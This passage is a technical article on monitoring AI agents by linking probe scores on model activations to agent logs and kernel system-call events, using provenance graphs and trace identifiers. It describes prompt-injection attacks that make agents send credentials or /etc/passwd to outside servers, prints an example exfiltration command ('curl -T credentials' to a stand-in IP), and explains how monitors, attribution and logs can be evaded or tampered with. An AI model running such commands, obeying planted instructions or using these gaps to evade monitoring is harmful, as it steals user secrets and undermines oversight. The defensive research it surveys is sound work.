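# Linking a model's internal states to host system activity when monitoring AI agents

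## The two traces an AI agent leaves

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that lets it run commands, edit files and use online services. The *Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (2026), from the US standards institute NIST, defines an agent system as at least one generative model plus "scaffolding software" that equips the model with tools. The model and the software leave different kinds of trace. Whenever the model chooses an action, it computes many intermediate numbers, called activations, on the hardware that runs it. When the software carries out the action, it starts programs, opens files or makes network connections on some machine, whose operating system can report each event.

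Security teams have used operating-system events for decades, while researchers began reading model activations more recently and mostly for other purposes. Linking the two would let an investigator trace a suspicious network connection back to the model's state when it requested the command that opened it, or start from a suspicious model state and check what then happened on disk. As of December 2026, no published study appears to have linked activations to system calls from the same agent. The nearest evidence comes from experiments that use only one of the traces and from a few systems that pair host events with the agent's text.

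### One turn of an agent

OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the inner loop of its coding agent, Codex, by following a request to add a diagram to a project's README, the file that introduces a software project. The agent software builds a prompt by combining the request with standing instructions, descriptions of the available tools and the name of the current folder. The server that runs the model converts the prompt into tokens, integers that each stand for a word or part of a word, and the model then produces new tokens one at a time. These tokens form either a message for the user, which ends the turn, or a tool call, which is a structured request for the software to run a command or use a service.

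The software, not the model, executes the tool call. It starts a shell, which starts the programs named in the command, and these may start further programs, known as child processes. When they finish, the software appends their output to the prompt and queries the model again. This repeats until the model answers with a message instead of a tool call, and a single turn can include hundreds of calls.

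Each new prompt contains the previous one as an exact prefix, which lets the server reuse earlier computation. A sentence that entered the context at the third tool call is still there at the thirtieth and can still affect it, unless the software has compressed the conversation into a summary. Restrictions also vary by tool within a turn. Codex runs its own shell tool in a sandbox, but tools from outside servers, which usually connect through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a plug-in standard, must enforce their own limits.

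### Three records of one step

Early in Bolin's example, the model outputs a request to run the shell command `cat README.md`, which reads the README. This step can appear in three records.

The internal record comes from inside the model. A language model is a stack of layers, and for each token every layer computes a vector, a long list of numbers, which it passes to the next layer. The vector at one layer for one token is an activation. Nobody can read such a vector by eye. A probe is a small classifier that does the reading: it takes activations and outputs a score for some property, such as harmful intent. Kramár, Engels and colleagues (2026), in *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini*, write the simplest version as an average over the n tokens of a text,

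score = (1/n) × (w·x₁ + w·x₂ + … + w·xₙ)

where xⱼ is the activation for token j and w is a list of weights. Training adjusts w, plus a constant, until labelled harmful texts score high and harmless ones low. In use, a further function squeezes the result into the range from 0 to 1, and a score above a chosen threshold raises an alarm. Probes are cheap because the model has to compute its activations anyway, so the only extra work is the small sum at the end. The internal record consists of activations, or of probe scores computed from them, stored with the request and token they belong to.

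The application record is what the agent software logs: prompts, model text, tool descriptions, tool calls and tool results. It links the model's internal states to the host's activity, since it contains the model's choice as text and the machine's activity starts from that text. In Codex, each tool call shares an identifier with its result. The record is incomplete about both the model's reasoning and the machine's activity. Codex stores the reasoning as a short summary beside an encrypted block that OpenAI's server can decrypt. If the agent runs `make`, which builds a program from its source code, the log will contain the command and its output, but not necessarily the files that `make` opened.

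Those files appear in the host record, which consists of the process, file and network events that the operating system reports for the agent and its child processes. The basic unit is the system call, a program's request to the operating system's kernel. On Linux, `execve` starts a program, `openat` opens a file and `connect` opens a network connection. The tool `strace` attaches to a running program and lists its system calls. *On the Effectiveness of Kernel-Level Evidence for Agent Security* (King, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) used `strace` on thousands of short agent sessions and collected about 3,500 events per session, with full file paths and command arguments.

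Newer monitors tend to use eBPF, a Linux facility that runs small verified programs inside the kernel to observe or block events. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) uses it to track every process an agent starts, record which process started which, and discard events from the rest of the machine. Companies mostly get host records from endpoint detection and response (EDR) software, which records activity on a machine, raises alarms, and can isolate or stop what it finds.

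With invented values, the step of reading the README might leave these entries:

| Record | Written by | One entry |
|---|---|---|
| Internal | Server running the model | request 52, token 1,904, layer 30, probe "harmful intent", score 0.03 |
| Application | Agent software | tool call 17, tool `shell`, command `cat README.md`, folder `/home/dev/project` |
| Host | Sensor in the operating system | 10:41:07.212, process 4127 (`cat`), parent 4126 (`bash`), `openat`, `/home/dev/project/README.md` |

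No identifier appears in all three rows. Linking activations to system calls depends on attribution, which means working out which session, request or tool call an event belongs to.

Single host events are hard to interpret in isolation, so analysts usually connect them in a provenance graph, which links processes, files and connections when one caused or supplied data to another. *Threat Detection and Investigation with System-level Provenance Graphs* (Li, Chen and colleagues, 2020) describes each event by its subject, object, time and operation. Subjects and objects are the graph's nodes, and events are its edges. A later event depends on an earlier one if the object of the earlier event is the subject of the later one. For example, if a shell starts a program at 10:42 and that program opens a connection at 10:43, the connection depends on the shell. Backward tracking collects everything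 that could have led to a suspicious event, and forward tracking collects everything the event could have affected.

### How a tool call comes to do harm

Content that an agent reads can lead it to make a harmful tool call. In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in that content to make the agent act against its user's wishes. NIST calls this "agent hijacking" when it leads the agent to take harmful actions. The attack works because a model receives instructions and data in the same stream of tokens and can't reliably tell them apart.

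For *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, Nakibly and Babo (2026) searched 142.7 million issues, pull requests and comments on the code-hosting site GitHub and found 43 real attacks, 19 of them attempts to steal secrets. GitHub never displays HTML comments, but an agent that fetches the raw text receives them. In July 2026, somebody filed what looked like an ordinary bug report with Google's Gemini CLI project. A hidden comment in it contained instructions for the project's own AI agent to copy an access token to a place where a later step could leak it. When Nakibly and Babo replayed the 43 attacks against five models, one small, fast model carried out 19% of them. After they removed the HTML comments, no model carried out any.

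An agent's tools can also be a source of harm. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (Li et al., 2026) reviews attacks through "Skills", add-on packages of instructions and scripts for agents. In one case, Cisco's AI security team found that the most popular community Skill on a major marketplace stole credentials while doing its advertised job. With a tampered package, the model may make an innocent tool call, and the package's own code can then carry out the theft.

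The attacker can also be the user. King and colleagues include sessions in which the user's own prompt requests harmful behaviour disguised as a benign task. In these sessions, nobody has hijacked the agent, and it does what its user wants.

The remaining source is the model's own unauthorized action. NIST's notice lists the risk that an uncompromised model may still threaten the confidentiality, availability or integrity of a system, for instance by satisfying its literal goal in a way nobody intended. King and colleagues understandably leave this case out of their threat model, because it has no attacker. For the same reason, a detector that looks for planted text or altered packages has nothing to find.

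### The running example

Suppose a user asks a coding agent to build a project. The project's README contains a hidden comment instructing agents to "register" the machine first by sending a credentials file to an outside server.

Zheng and colleagues ran a similar test. They told an agent to download and build a project written in C, whose README pointed to a web page with a hidden prompt. The agent read `/etc/passwd`, the Linux list of user accounts, and sent it to a collection server, using a command disguised as a build step. The attack left 521 events in their trace.

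In the running example, exposure occurs when the agent reads the README, which puts the hidden comment into the model's context. If the model acts on the comment by writing a tool call that uploads the credentials file, that is commitment. The shell then starts a transfer program, which opens the file and connects to the server. Afterward, the agent builds the project and truthfully reports success.

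One stage can occur without the next. A model that reads the comment and ignores it has had exposure without commitment, and a monitor that raised an alarm over every such reading would soon frustrate its users with false alarms. Commitment can also occur without damage. In *You Told Me to Do It* (Kao, Li et al., 2026), an agent named OpenDevin followed planted instructions of this sort. It located the private file and issued the exact copy command, and the transfer failed only because its container blocked outgoing traffic. Another variant is harder to detect because the README only asks the agent to run `setup.sh`, and the upload is a line inside that script. The tool call then looks like any other installation step.

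Kao and colleagues put such instructions into 500 real READMEs and got private files out in up to 85% of trials. Their agent ran on Claude Sonnet 3.7, a model from early 2025, so the figure is more a historical result than a current estimate. None of their 15 human readers recognised the planted instructions as suspicious, but the readers had been asked to review the text for clarity, with no mention of security. Nakibly and Babo checked the READMEs of GitHub's two million most-starred projects and found attacks in only four, with two distinct payloads among them. The attack in the running example is therefore rare but damaging, which affects what a useful detector has to do.

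### Scores, thresholds and false alarms

Most detectors output a score, whether their input is activations or system calls. For example, a detector might give five harmful agent sessions scores of 0.90, 0.80, 0.70, 0.60 and 0.30, and five harmless ones 0.65, 0.40, 0.20, 0.15 and 0.10.

With the alarm threshold at 0.50, four of the five harmful sessions trigger an alarm, so the detection rate is 80%. One of the five harmless sessions also triggers one, so the false-positive rate is 20%. Raising the threshold to 0.68 removes the false alarm but lowers the detection rate to 60%.

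AUROC measures the detector's performance without requiring a threshold. It is the probability that a random harmful case scores above a random harmless one. The five harmful and five harmless sessions form 25 pairs. The top three harmful sessions score above all five harmless ones, the session at 0.60 scores above four, and the one at 0.30 scores above three. The harmful session scores higher in 22 of the 25 pairs, which gives an AUROC of 0.88. Random scoring would give 0.5, and a perfect detector would give 1.

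An AUROC of 0.88 is good for ranking cases, but half of the sessions in this example are harmful, and harmful sessions are much rarer in real traffic. Over 10,000 sessions, ten of them harmful, the same detector with its threshold at 0.50 would catch eight and raise 1,998 false alarms. Its AUROC would still be 0.88, because AUROC does not depend on how common harm is. Reducing the false alarms to about ten would require a false-positive rate near 0.1%. For anyone who has to answer the alarms, the detection rate at a very low false-positive rate is more informative than the AUROC.

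### From system-call sequences to provenance graphs

The idea of detecting intruders by their system calls goes back at least to *A Sense of Self for Unix Processes* (Forrest, Hofmeyr and colleagues, 1996), which based it on the immune system's distinction between self and other. The method slides a short window along the calls of a healthy program and records which calls follow which, and at what distance. Any pair missing from this list counts as a mismatch. In the paper's example, changing one call in a sequence of eight produces 4 mismatches out of a possible 18, or 22%.

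For the mail program `sendmail`, 112 test messages generated over 1.5 million system calls, but with a window of six calls, these produced only about 1,500 entries. Normal behaviour was far more regular than expected. Real attacks could be distinguished from it, though some only barely. With a window of 11, one attack produced 5.2% mismatches and another 0.3%. In a follow-up, Hofmeyr, Forrest and Somayaji reported that short sequences of system calls separate normal from abnormal behaviour in several common Unix programs.

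The method suits agents poorly for two reasons. It ignores the arguments of each call, so reading a README and reading a credentials file look alike. It also assumes, as Forrest and colleagues point out, that a program's code is mostly static, with system calls at fixed places in it. An agent keeps composing new commands as it runs. Zheng and colleagues compare its plans to source code created at runtime, and such a program may have no stable list of normal sequences to record.

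Provenance graphs record which files, processes and addresses were involved, details that the sequences discard. Early systems such as BackTracker helped investigators after an attack, while *SLEUTH* (2018) aimed to detect attacks in real time. The approach has always had two problems. The first is the volume of logs, which an estimate cited in the survey by Li and colleagues puts at 70 petabytes a year for a bank with 20,000 machines. The second is false dependence. If a process reads fifty files and then opens a connection, as a long-running agent does, the graph shows all fifty as possible sources of whatever it sent. Tracking data inside each process removes many of the false links, but the survey puts the overhead at between twofold and tenfold.

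In *MINOS*, Wang, Li and colleagues (2026) use language models to find attack events in a machine's log. They note that these events usually make up less than 0.001% of the log, and that many look harmless on their own. A Windows script that creates a scheduled task, for example, might be routine administration or an intruder's way of keeping access. In their system, several agents debate each event and decide where to look next. Over 14 attack scenarios, it recovered 92% of the attack events on average, and 64% of the events it flagged belonged to the attack. This is a strong result for reconstructing an attack, but the system needs an alarm to start from.

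### Probing neural networks

Probes have a shorter history. In *Understanding intermediate layers using linear classifier probes*, Alain and Bengio (2016) attached a separate linear classifier to each layer of image-recognition networks and trained it to name the object in the picture, without changing the network. They compared probes to thermometers placed at many points in a machine. In ResNet-50, the probes' error fell almost steadily with depth, from 94% after the first block of layers to 31% after the last.

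A later layer cannot contain more information about the picture than an earlier one, but a simple classifier can use the information more easily. Alain and Bengio compare a photograph of a lion with the same file as raw digits. The digits contain at least as much information, but a person can quickly recognize the lion only in the photograph. The same distinction applies to a probe for harmful intent. A high score means that something resembling the training examples is easy to read off at that layer, not that the model will act on it. A low score may only mean that the information is there in a form the probe cannot use.

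Ten years later, Kramár and colleagues at Google DeepMind describe probes that detect cyberattack requests to the company's Gemini models, and this work has contributed to a live deployment. They found that probes trained on short prompts did poorly on long ones, and much of their effort went into designs that handle long prompts better. Agents normally have long prompts because their context grows with every tool call. The probes also read only the model's input. Kramár and colleagues leave probes on the output, where tool calls appear, to future work.

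## How an activation is matched to a system call

An activation is a row of numbers on the model's server that belongs to one token of one request. That request produces a tool call, the tool call starts a process, and that process or a child process makes the system call. Linking the activation to the system call requires matching each step to the next, and if any match fails, the two can't be linked.

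The operating system reports the ID of the process that caused each event and the parent of each new process. The harder steps are finding which request a row of activations belongs to and which process a tool call started.

### Finding the request that owns a row

Serving engines run many requests through the model together to keep the hardware busy. *Undercurrent* (Khatri, 2026) describes how this affects activations in vLLM, a popular open-source engine. At each step, every layer processes one table with T rows and d columns, where d is the length of an activation. The rows come from the requests the scheduler picked for that step. A request may supply hundreds of rows while the model processes its prompt, but it supplies only one per step while the model generates its answer. Requests join and leave between steps, and the engine splits long prompts over several steps, so the same row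 can belong to different requests at different steps.

Undercurrent, an open-source library that runs probes inside such engines, uses the scheduler's records to work out which request each row belongs to. For each request in the step, taken in row order, it needs the prompt length P, the number of tokens c that the model has already processed, and the number n that it will process in this step. The request's rows then hold token positions c to c + n − 1, counting from zero. Positions below P hold prompt tokens, and the rest hold tokens the model wrote.

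A small batch with three users' requests might look like this:

| Request | P | c | n | Rows | Positions | Content |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | 6 | 7 | 1 | 0 | 7 | second token of the answer |
| B | 10 | 4 | 3 | 1–3 | 4–6 | middle of the prompt |
| C | 3 | 3 | 1 | 4 | 3 | first token of the answer |

Suppose A now finishes. In the next step, B occupies rows 0 to 2 with the end of its prompt, and C moves up to row 3. Software that still assigned row 0 to A would record the model's internal states for one customer's request in another customer's security log. Undercurrent therefore repeats the calculation at every step and raises an error if it encounters an unknown request.

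A monitor can also pick the right row but read it from the wrong table. For Llama-family models, vLLM returns two tables per layer. The obvious one holds only the layer's latest contribution, but probes usually read the running total, which Undercurrent gets by adding the two tables together. To check this, Khatri ran tiny random models through both vLLM and a simpler library that handles one text at a time, and required the activations to agree within 0.1%. Reading the wrong table would give an error about as large as the values themselves.

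*Enabling Performant and Flexible Model-Internal Observability for LLM Inference* (Yu, Xiong and colleagues, 2026) presents DMI-Lib, a tool that solves the same problem. The inference engine schedules the requests and tokens for each step before running it, so DMI-Lib puts that list in a queue on the CPU, copies the raw activations into a buffer on the GPU, and pairs the two afterwards. When a model is split over several GPUs, each GPU exports its fragment of the activations with a record of where it fits, and the fragments can be reassembled using their shared request and token identifiers. Matching activation rows to requests is therefore largely solved for open-weight models.

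In an agent session, the engine reuses computation from earlier requests, so a new request starts with c well above zero. The engine therefore computes the activations for a hidden comment only once, in the first request that contains it. If the model acts on the comment three requests later, exposure and commitment have different request identifiers, and only the session connects them.

### Probes that can stop a request

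Undercurrent runs a probe either inline or asynchronously. The engine waits for an inline probe's verdict and ends the request if the verdict is bad. An asynchronous probe receives copies of the activations through a queue while the model keeps generating, so it can report a problem but not stop the request.

An inline probe delays each step by roughly the number of activations it reads multiplied by the time it takes to copy one to the CPU and score it. Khatri measured this with GPT-2, a small model from 2019, on a laptop without a GPU. Eight small neural-network probes took 1.28 milliseconds per token, about 2.7% of the time the model needed to produce one. Models produce tokens much faster on GPUs, so the same probes would take a larger share of the time, but Khatri gives no GPU figure.

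An asynchronous probe can lose data if it falls behind the model. In one test, Khatri slowed a probe to about half the model's speed and gave it a queue of four entries. When Undercurrent dropped activations that did not fit in the queue, the model ran at its normal speed, but the probe missed about half of the 1,008 activations. Making the model wait instead prevented any loss but cut throughput by 53%. A security team would at least want the number of dropped activations in its log, since otherwise a gap in the data looks the same as a quiet period.

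The library is more limited on vLLM. Khatri labels its vLLM support experimental and has validated it with only one worker process. It needs vLLM's slower "eager" mode, because the usual speed-up replays a recorded sequence of GPU operations and skips the Python code that captures activations. A request can stop only at the next step, so the model writes at least one more token after the alarm. If the engine waits for a slow probe, every user in the batch waits too. DMI-Lib keeps the speed-up, but it exports data and other software has to make the decisions.

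One extra token is often harmless with an agent, because the agent software cannot run a half-written tool call. A probe that fires early in the call leaves enough time to stop it, but if the probe has to score the complete call, the server must hold back the response until the probe has scored it.

### Exact identifiers in the agent's log

Matching a model request to a tool call is the easiest step, because the agent software can log the link itself. Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, its coding agent, lists a `session.id` for the session, a `prompt.id` for everything triggered by one user prompt, a `request_id` for each model request and a `tool_use_id` for each tool call. Since version 2.1.310, the log entry for a tool's result also includes the `request_id` of the response that contained the call. When the agent delegates work to a subagent, Anthropic's tracing feature records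 the subagent's requests and tool calls under the parent's tool call.

The tracing feature comes close to linking a model's internal states to activity on the host. With tracing on, every shell command inherits an environment variable, `TRACEPARENT`, which identifies the trace and the tool execution that started the command. Each model request sent directly to Anthropic's interface has a header with the same trace identifier, which could be used to join records from Anthropic's servers with records from the user's machine. A host sensor would have to read the variable when a process starts, since ordinary process events don't include it, and a hostile program could delete or change it. Tracing is also in beta and off by default.

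Other products, including GitHub's Copilot agent, use the same W3C standard for trace identifiers. GitHub's *Built-in telemetry support* explains how an application passes its trace to the agent. *AgentTrace* (AlSayyad, Huang and Pal, 2026) proposes a common log format in which each entry has a trace identifier, a span identifier for the individual operation and a UTC timestamp. The format's "cognitive" category holds prompts, model outputs and written reasoning, but not activations.

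Operating system events tend to lack an identifier that links them to a specific tool call. In *Mind the Gap*, Holmwood (2026) recorded the same Claude Code tool call in the network traffic, the agent's log and the Windows process events. The traffic and the log shared a tool-call identifier, but the process events had none. Holmwood matched the process events to the call by making the model put a unique marker in the command, which works in an experiment but not with an uncooperative agent.

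The times lined up well. In the log, the tool finished at 23.642 seconds past the minute after running for 373 milliseconds, so it started at about 23.269. Windows recorded the start of PowerShell at 23.284 and of its child, `cmd.exe`, at 23.534. With one tool call on one machine, time and parentage are enough to find the right processes among the session's roughly 900 process events.

### Inferring the match from outside the agent

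AgentSight, the eBPF monitor by Zheng and colleagues, infers the match instead of relying on the agent's log. It hooks the functions that encrypt and decrypt network traffic on the agent's machine, so it can read the model's responses as plain text, and it collects process, file and network events from the kernel. It then combines three signals:

- **Process lineage:** an event counts only if its process descends from the agent.
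- **Time:** it looks for events within 100 to 500 milliseconds after a model response.
- **Arguments:** it compares file names, addresses and commands in the response with the arguments of the system calls that follow.

A second language model then reads the combined trace and judges whether the activity fits the task.

In the README attack described earlier, AgentSight merged 521 raw events into 37. The second model gave the trace a high attack score because sending the list of user accounts to a server had nothing to do with building a C project. This shows the two kinds of evidence working better together, but in only one attack. Zheng and colleagues don't report how many of AgentSight's links were correct, so their results don't show how often it would attribute system activity to the wrong response.

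The monitoring itself adds little running time. On three Claude Code tasks, each run three times, AgentSight added 3.4%, 4.9% and 0.4%, an average of 2.9%. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) measured AgentSight's overhead again on similar tasks with a newer version of Claude Code and reported 4.5%, 2.5% and 1.7%.

Each signal can mislead. Lineage also captures programs that no tool call explains. In one of Holmwood's runs, 27 such programs started under the Claude process. Most were housekeeping by the agent software, such as `git` commands and a search for other editors on the machine. One was the Windows calculator, which opened because PowerShell treated a semicolon in an ordinary sentence as the end of a command. Lineage correctly assigns all 27 programs to the agent, but a time window could wrongly link the housekeeping to whatever the model had just written.

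The window also misses slow work, such as a build that opens a file a minute after the response that started it. Zheng and colleagues also traced six agents working in parallel, which can produce several responses within half a second.

Argument matching depends on the command's text staying the same between the model's response and the system call. Holmwood had the model write a command containing the variable `$env:COMPUTERNAME`. PowerShell replaced the variable with the machine's name before starting the program, so the log and the kernel recorded different text. In the `setup.sh` variant of the running example, the response mentions only the script, and the outside server's address first appears in the system call. Lineage would still connect the response and the system call, because the script's processes descend from the agent.

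### Files, daemons and labels in the kernel

Matching by lineage fails when the harmful process does not descend from the agent. Bao and colleagues give the example of an agent that writes a malicious script and adds a line to the crontab, the Linux schedule for recurring jobs. An hour later `cron`, a background service, runs the script, which opens a connection to the attacker. `cron` is not a child process of the agent, and by then the time window has long closed and the agent may have exited.

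AgentLoupe labels the agent's process when the process sends a new prompt to the model, and the kernel monitor then passes the label along. Child processes inherit the label. A file receives it when a labelled process writes to the file, and so does any process that later opens or executes that file. Network connections also carry the label. In the crontab attack, the script kept its label until `cron` ran it, and AgentLoupe traced the connection back to the conversation that had produced the script. In a second test, one session planted an instruction in a file that agents read at startup, a later session followed it, and the file's label linked the two sessions.

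Bao and colleagues argue from AgentSight's design that it would miss both attacks, but they leave a side-by-side test for future work. They also haven't measured how often labels spread too far or get lost. Spreading too far is the bigger worry because a long-running agent touches many files, and each could pass the label to unrelated programs. AgentLoupe limits this by starting a new label with each independent prompt and recording its link to the previous one. One label can still cover several model responses (five in the crontab case), so identifying a particular activation requires a further match within that group. Labelling raised overhead to between 4.5% and 8%.

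*Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) tracks only processes and files, without reading the model's traffic, at an overhead of 0.2% to 3.5%. Linux reuses process numbers, so "process 4132" can mean two different programs on the same day, and any joined record needs to tell them apart. One version of Agent-Warden does this by attaching its label to the kernel's data structure for the process, which disappears when the process ends. A log can achieve much the same by storing the process's start time next to its number.

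A simpler method is to run each agent session in its own container, so that every event inside the container belongs to that session. This identifies which session caused an event, but not which tool call. In *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026), the agent acts through a runtime that carries out each operation and records the model request and tool that led to each effect. These links are exact, but they cover only operations that pass through the runtime, and Zhang does not claim that the runtime confines programs as a kernel would.

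### Extending the provenance graph to the model

These matches let a provenance graph continue past the agent's process into the model's context. In the running example, the graph would have an edge from the README to the request that contained it, one from that request to the tool call, and then the usual edges to the shell, the credentials file and the outside server.

The edge through the model is the weakest. In *Ghost in the Agent*, Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026) distinguish content that the agent copies or paraphrases from content that only changes its decision. For example, a poisoned web page might make an agent call a different tool even if none of the page's words appear in the call. They write that such influence is hard to attribute from logs without access to the model's internal states. Their system still works from logs. It tests whether the tool call would still follow if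 neutral text replaced the suspicious content. On their benchmark of 400 scenarios, which also includes copied content and content stored for later sessions, 92% of the flows the system flagged were real, and it found 94% of the real flows.

Probe scores could provide some direct evidence for the edge, such as a high score on the hidden comment followed by a high score on the tool call. This is an inference, and the evidence would be weaker than a replacement test's, because two high scores in a row don't prove that one caused the other.

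Existing graphs include an agent's text but not the model's activations. *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents* (Li, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) includes nodes for an agent's goals, context, reasoning and decisions, and builds them with a plug-in for the agent software OpenClaw, which normally has no access to activations. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) reports that no benchmark in its catalogue tests the complete chain of provenance.

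### Who holds which record

Most agents don't run on the same machine as their model. Large models need expensive GPUs that many users share, and companies often keep the weights secret. The tools have to run where the files are, usually on a laptop, a company server or a temporary sandbox. The records of activations and system calls therefore end up on different machines, often with different owners.

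| Layout | Internal record | Application and host records | Who could join them |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model and agent on one self-hosted machine | Operator | Operator | The operator, with one clock |
| Self-hosted model, separate sandboxes | Operator, on the model server | Operator, on the agent and sandbox machines | The operator, if identifiers travel between machines |
| Model behind a provider's interface | Provider | Customer | Neither, unless one shares data with the other |

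An operator could combine Undercurrent with an eBPF monitor on a single self-hosted machine today, but an agent that gains administrator rights can reach all the records at once. Separate sandboxes protect the model server's records better and are more realistic for a company with many agents. The operator then has to send the request identifier with each tool call and have the sandbox store it with its events.

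When a customer uses a model through a provider's interface, the customer cannot see the model's activations and the provider cannot see the customer's system calls. The two can already share identifiers, for example through Anthropic's trace header, although Claude Code does not send this header when the customer reaches the model through a third-party provider. They do not yet exchange monitoring data. The provider could return a probe score with each response, much as Undercurrent's example server returns its verdicts with the model's text. Alternatively, the customer could send host alarms to the provider, who would look up the matching request.

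There is a small precedent for recording a provider's judgement in a customer's log. When Claude refuses a request, the response can include a category such as "cyber", which Claude Code can log with the request identifier. Anthropic does not document what produces the category.

Some providers also run the agent's machine. Claude Code's cloud sessions, for example, can run in environments that Anthropic hosts, so Anthropic operates both the model and the computer where the tools run. In principle, it could do every step of the match between activations and system calls itself.

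### A joined record for the running example

Continuing with invented values, suppose the README reached the model in request 53 and the model answered with the upload. The record of the attack might read:

| Step | Entry | Basis of the link to the previous step |
|---|---|---|
| Exposure | request 53, prompt tokens 2,310–2,356, layer 30, probe "embedded instruction", highest score 0.91 | – |
| Commitment | request 53, answer tokens 0–38, layer 30, probe "harmful intent", mean score 0.84 | Same request |
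| Tool call | call 18, tool `shell`, command `curl -T credentials 203.0.113.9` | Request identifier in the agent's log |
| Process | 10:41:12.431, process 4131 (`bash`), parent 3990 (agent) | Trace identifier, or inference from lineage, time and arguments |
| Child process | 10:41:12.446, process 4132 (`curl`), parent 4131 | Kernel |
| System calls | 10:41:12.480, `openat`, `/home/dev/project/credentials`; 10:41:12.530, `connect`, 203.0.113.9 | Process number and start time |

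Any real record should include the last column, so that an investigator knows whether each link is based on an identifier or a guess. The link from tool call to process is the most likely to be a guess.

Even an exact identifier is reliable only if the software that logs it has not been tampered with. Holmwood altered Claude Code's program file so that it logged a harmless file name in place of the real one, and the network traffic exposed the change. A second alteration changed the command after the software had logged it. The traffic and the log then matched, and only the host record showed which file the command had touched. Both alterations require control of the user's machine, so they are more of a concern after a break-in than in an ordinary prompt injection.

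### Clocks and remote tools

AgentSight can use a window of a few hundred milliseconds because it records the model's responses and the system calls on the same machine. Matching by time is riskier when the internal record comes from a distant server. Suppose the server finishes the response at 10:41:12.400 and the sandbox's clock runs 300 milliseconds slow. The connection at 10:41:12.530 would be logged at 10:41:12.230, before the response that caused it. Synchronized clocks reduce this error, but identifiers avoid the problem because the links show the order of the steps.

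Claude Code numbers its events, but the numbering restarts with each new process, so a resumed session can contain the same number twice. Anthropic recommends sorting events by timestamp first and using the number only to break ties.

The chain from activation to system call also breaks when a tool runs on an outside MCP server, because the user's machine records the connection to the server but not what happens there. Holmwood built an MCP tool that did nothing except report success, and the agent's log recorded a successful call. A tool that did far more than it reported would leave the same kind of log entry. Claude Code can send its trace header to MCP servers that it reaches over HTTP, so a cooperative server could store its own events under the same trace, but a malicious server wouldn't.

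### What it costs to keep activations

Raw activations are large. Gemma 4 E4B, a small open-weight model, has 42 layers and activations of 2,560 numbers, according to *The cognitive companion* (2026). One token therefore produces 42 × 2,560 = 107,520 numbers, or about 215 kilobytes at two bytes each. For a session in which the model processes 100,000 tokens, the options compare as follows:

| What the operator keeps | Size per session |
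|---|---|
| All 42 layers, two bytes per number | 21.5 GB |
| One layer, two bytes per number | 512 MB |
| One probe score per token, four bytes each | 0.4 MB |
| Host record of 3,500 events, assuming 500 bytes each | 1.75 MB |

Undercurrent copies activations at four bytes per number, and storing them in that form would double the first two figures. Larger models would need more storage because their activations are longer and they usually have more layers. A thousand such sessions a day would produce 21.5 terabytes of raw activations, compared with 400 megabytes of scores before adding identifiers.

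Moving the data also slows the server. When Yu and colleagues captured a modest selection of activations, a live vLLM server slowed by about 6% on average. When they captured everything at 325 points in the model while it read prompts, the connection between GPU and CPU was too slow for the volume of data, and the overhead reached 575% to 726%. Simpler tools cause serious delays at much lighter loads. The plug-in from *vLLM Hook v1* (2026) saves chosen internal states for later analysis. With the version that Yu and colleagues tested, the first token of an answer took 10 to 15 times as long as normal to arrive, even at one request per second.

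Scoring activations immediately and then discarding them avoids most of this overhead. *GateWatch* (2026) does this inside the serving engine. It reads each layer's output as the layer runs and stores only one bit for each target feature. The disadvantage is that investigators cannot apply a better probe to the activations later.

An operator who has the model's weights can save storage by keeping the tokens, which take a few bytes each, instead of the activations, and running the same model over them again when an alarm comes in. The recomputed activations may differ slightly from the originals because of rounding, and the operator has to keep old versions of the model.

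### Retention and privacy

A joined record is more sensitive than any of its parts because it connects what a person typed, a classifier's guess about harmful intent, and the files that a program then opened. Deleting the prompt does not make the rest anonymous, because the activations and scores derive from it. Undercurrent's logs describe activations only by their shape and number type. Khatri recommends that operators disclose what they monitor and keep the data only as long as they need it.

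Privacy settings can also make matching less reliable. By default, Claude Code's traces include identifiers but leave out prompt text and the details of tool calls. Argument matching needs the commands in those details, so it can't be used unless an administrator turns them on.

Delayed attacks make it hard to choose a retention period. The crontab job in Bao and colleagues' test ran after an hour, but an attacker could as easily schedule one for a month later. If the operator deletes scores and tokens after two weeks, the label on the script will still identify the right conversation, but no record will remain of the model's state when it wrote the script.

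## What each record can show in principle

Even perfectly matched records can be incomplete. Activations have a theoretical limit that does not apply to system calls, and this limit affects what an operator can gain from joining the two.

### The information ceiling

A model's activations depend only on its weights and the tokens it has read. Gao (2026), in *From Probe Scores to Alarm Policies*, derives a limit from this. Let O be everything the model has read at the moment of monitoring, A its activations, and Y the outcome to predict, such as whether the agent will upload the credentials file. The model is a fixed function f, with A = f(O), and therefore

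I(Y; A | O) = 0

Here I is mutual information, which measures how much knowing one quantity reduces uncertainty about another, and the bar means "given". Once an observer has the full text, the activations don't reduce uncertainty about the outcome. This is because any rule h that raises alarms from activations can be turned into a rule for text, h(f(O)), which runs the model on the text and applies h to the result. The two rules raise exactly the same alarms, so the best possible reader of the text does at least as well as the best possible probe. Gao calls this the information ceiling.

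Suppose two sessions have identical contexts until the model starts its next tool call. Models usually choose each token partly at random, so one session may continue with the upload and the other with an ordinary build command. Apart from rounding differences, the activations before that choice are the same in both sessions, so no probe reading them could tell the sessions apart. Once the model has written the upload command, the text differs as well as the activations.

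The argument predates AI agents. *Information-Theoretic Probing for Linguistic Structure* (Pimentel, Valvoda and colleagues, 2020) proved that the representations of BERT, an early language model, can't provide more information about a word's grammatical role than the sentence itself. It concluded that probing for linguistic properties "may not be a well grounded enterprise at all" and called for a formal definition of how easy information is to extract.

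### Why probes can still help

The rule h(f(O)) contains a complete copy of the model, which an analyst reading a log does not have in their head. Xu, Zhao and colleagues (2020) formalize this objection in *A Theory of Usable Information Under Computational Constraints*. Like the raw digits of Alain and Bengio's lion photograph, an encrypted message contains all the information in the readable version, but a reader must decrypt it before using it.

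Their measure starts from a set V of predictors that the observer can afford to use, for example all linear classifiers. The uncertainty H_V is the smallest average prediction error, measured in log-probability, that any predictor in V can achieve. The usable information in X about Y is then

I_V(X → Y) = H_V(Y) − H_V(Y | X)

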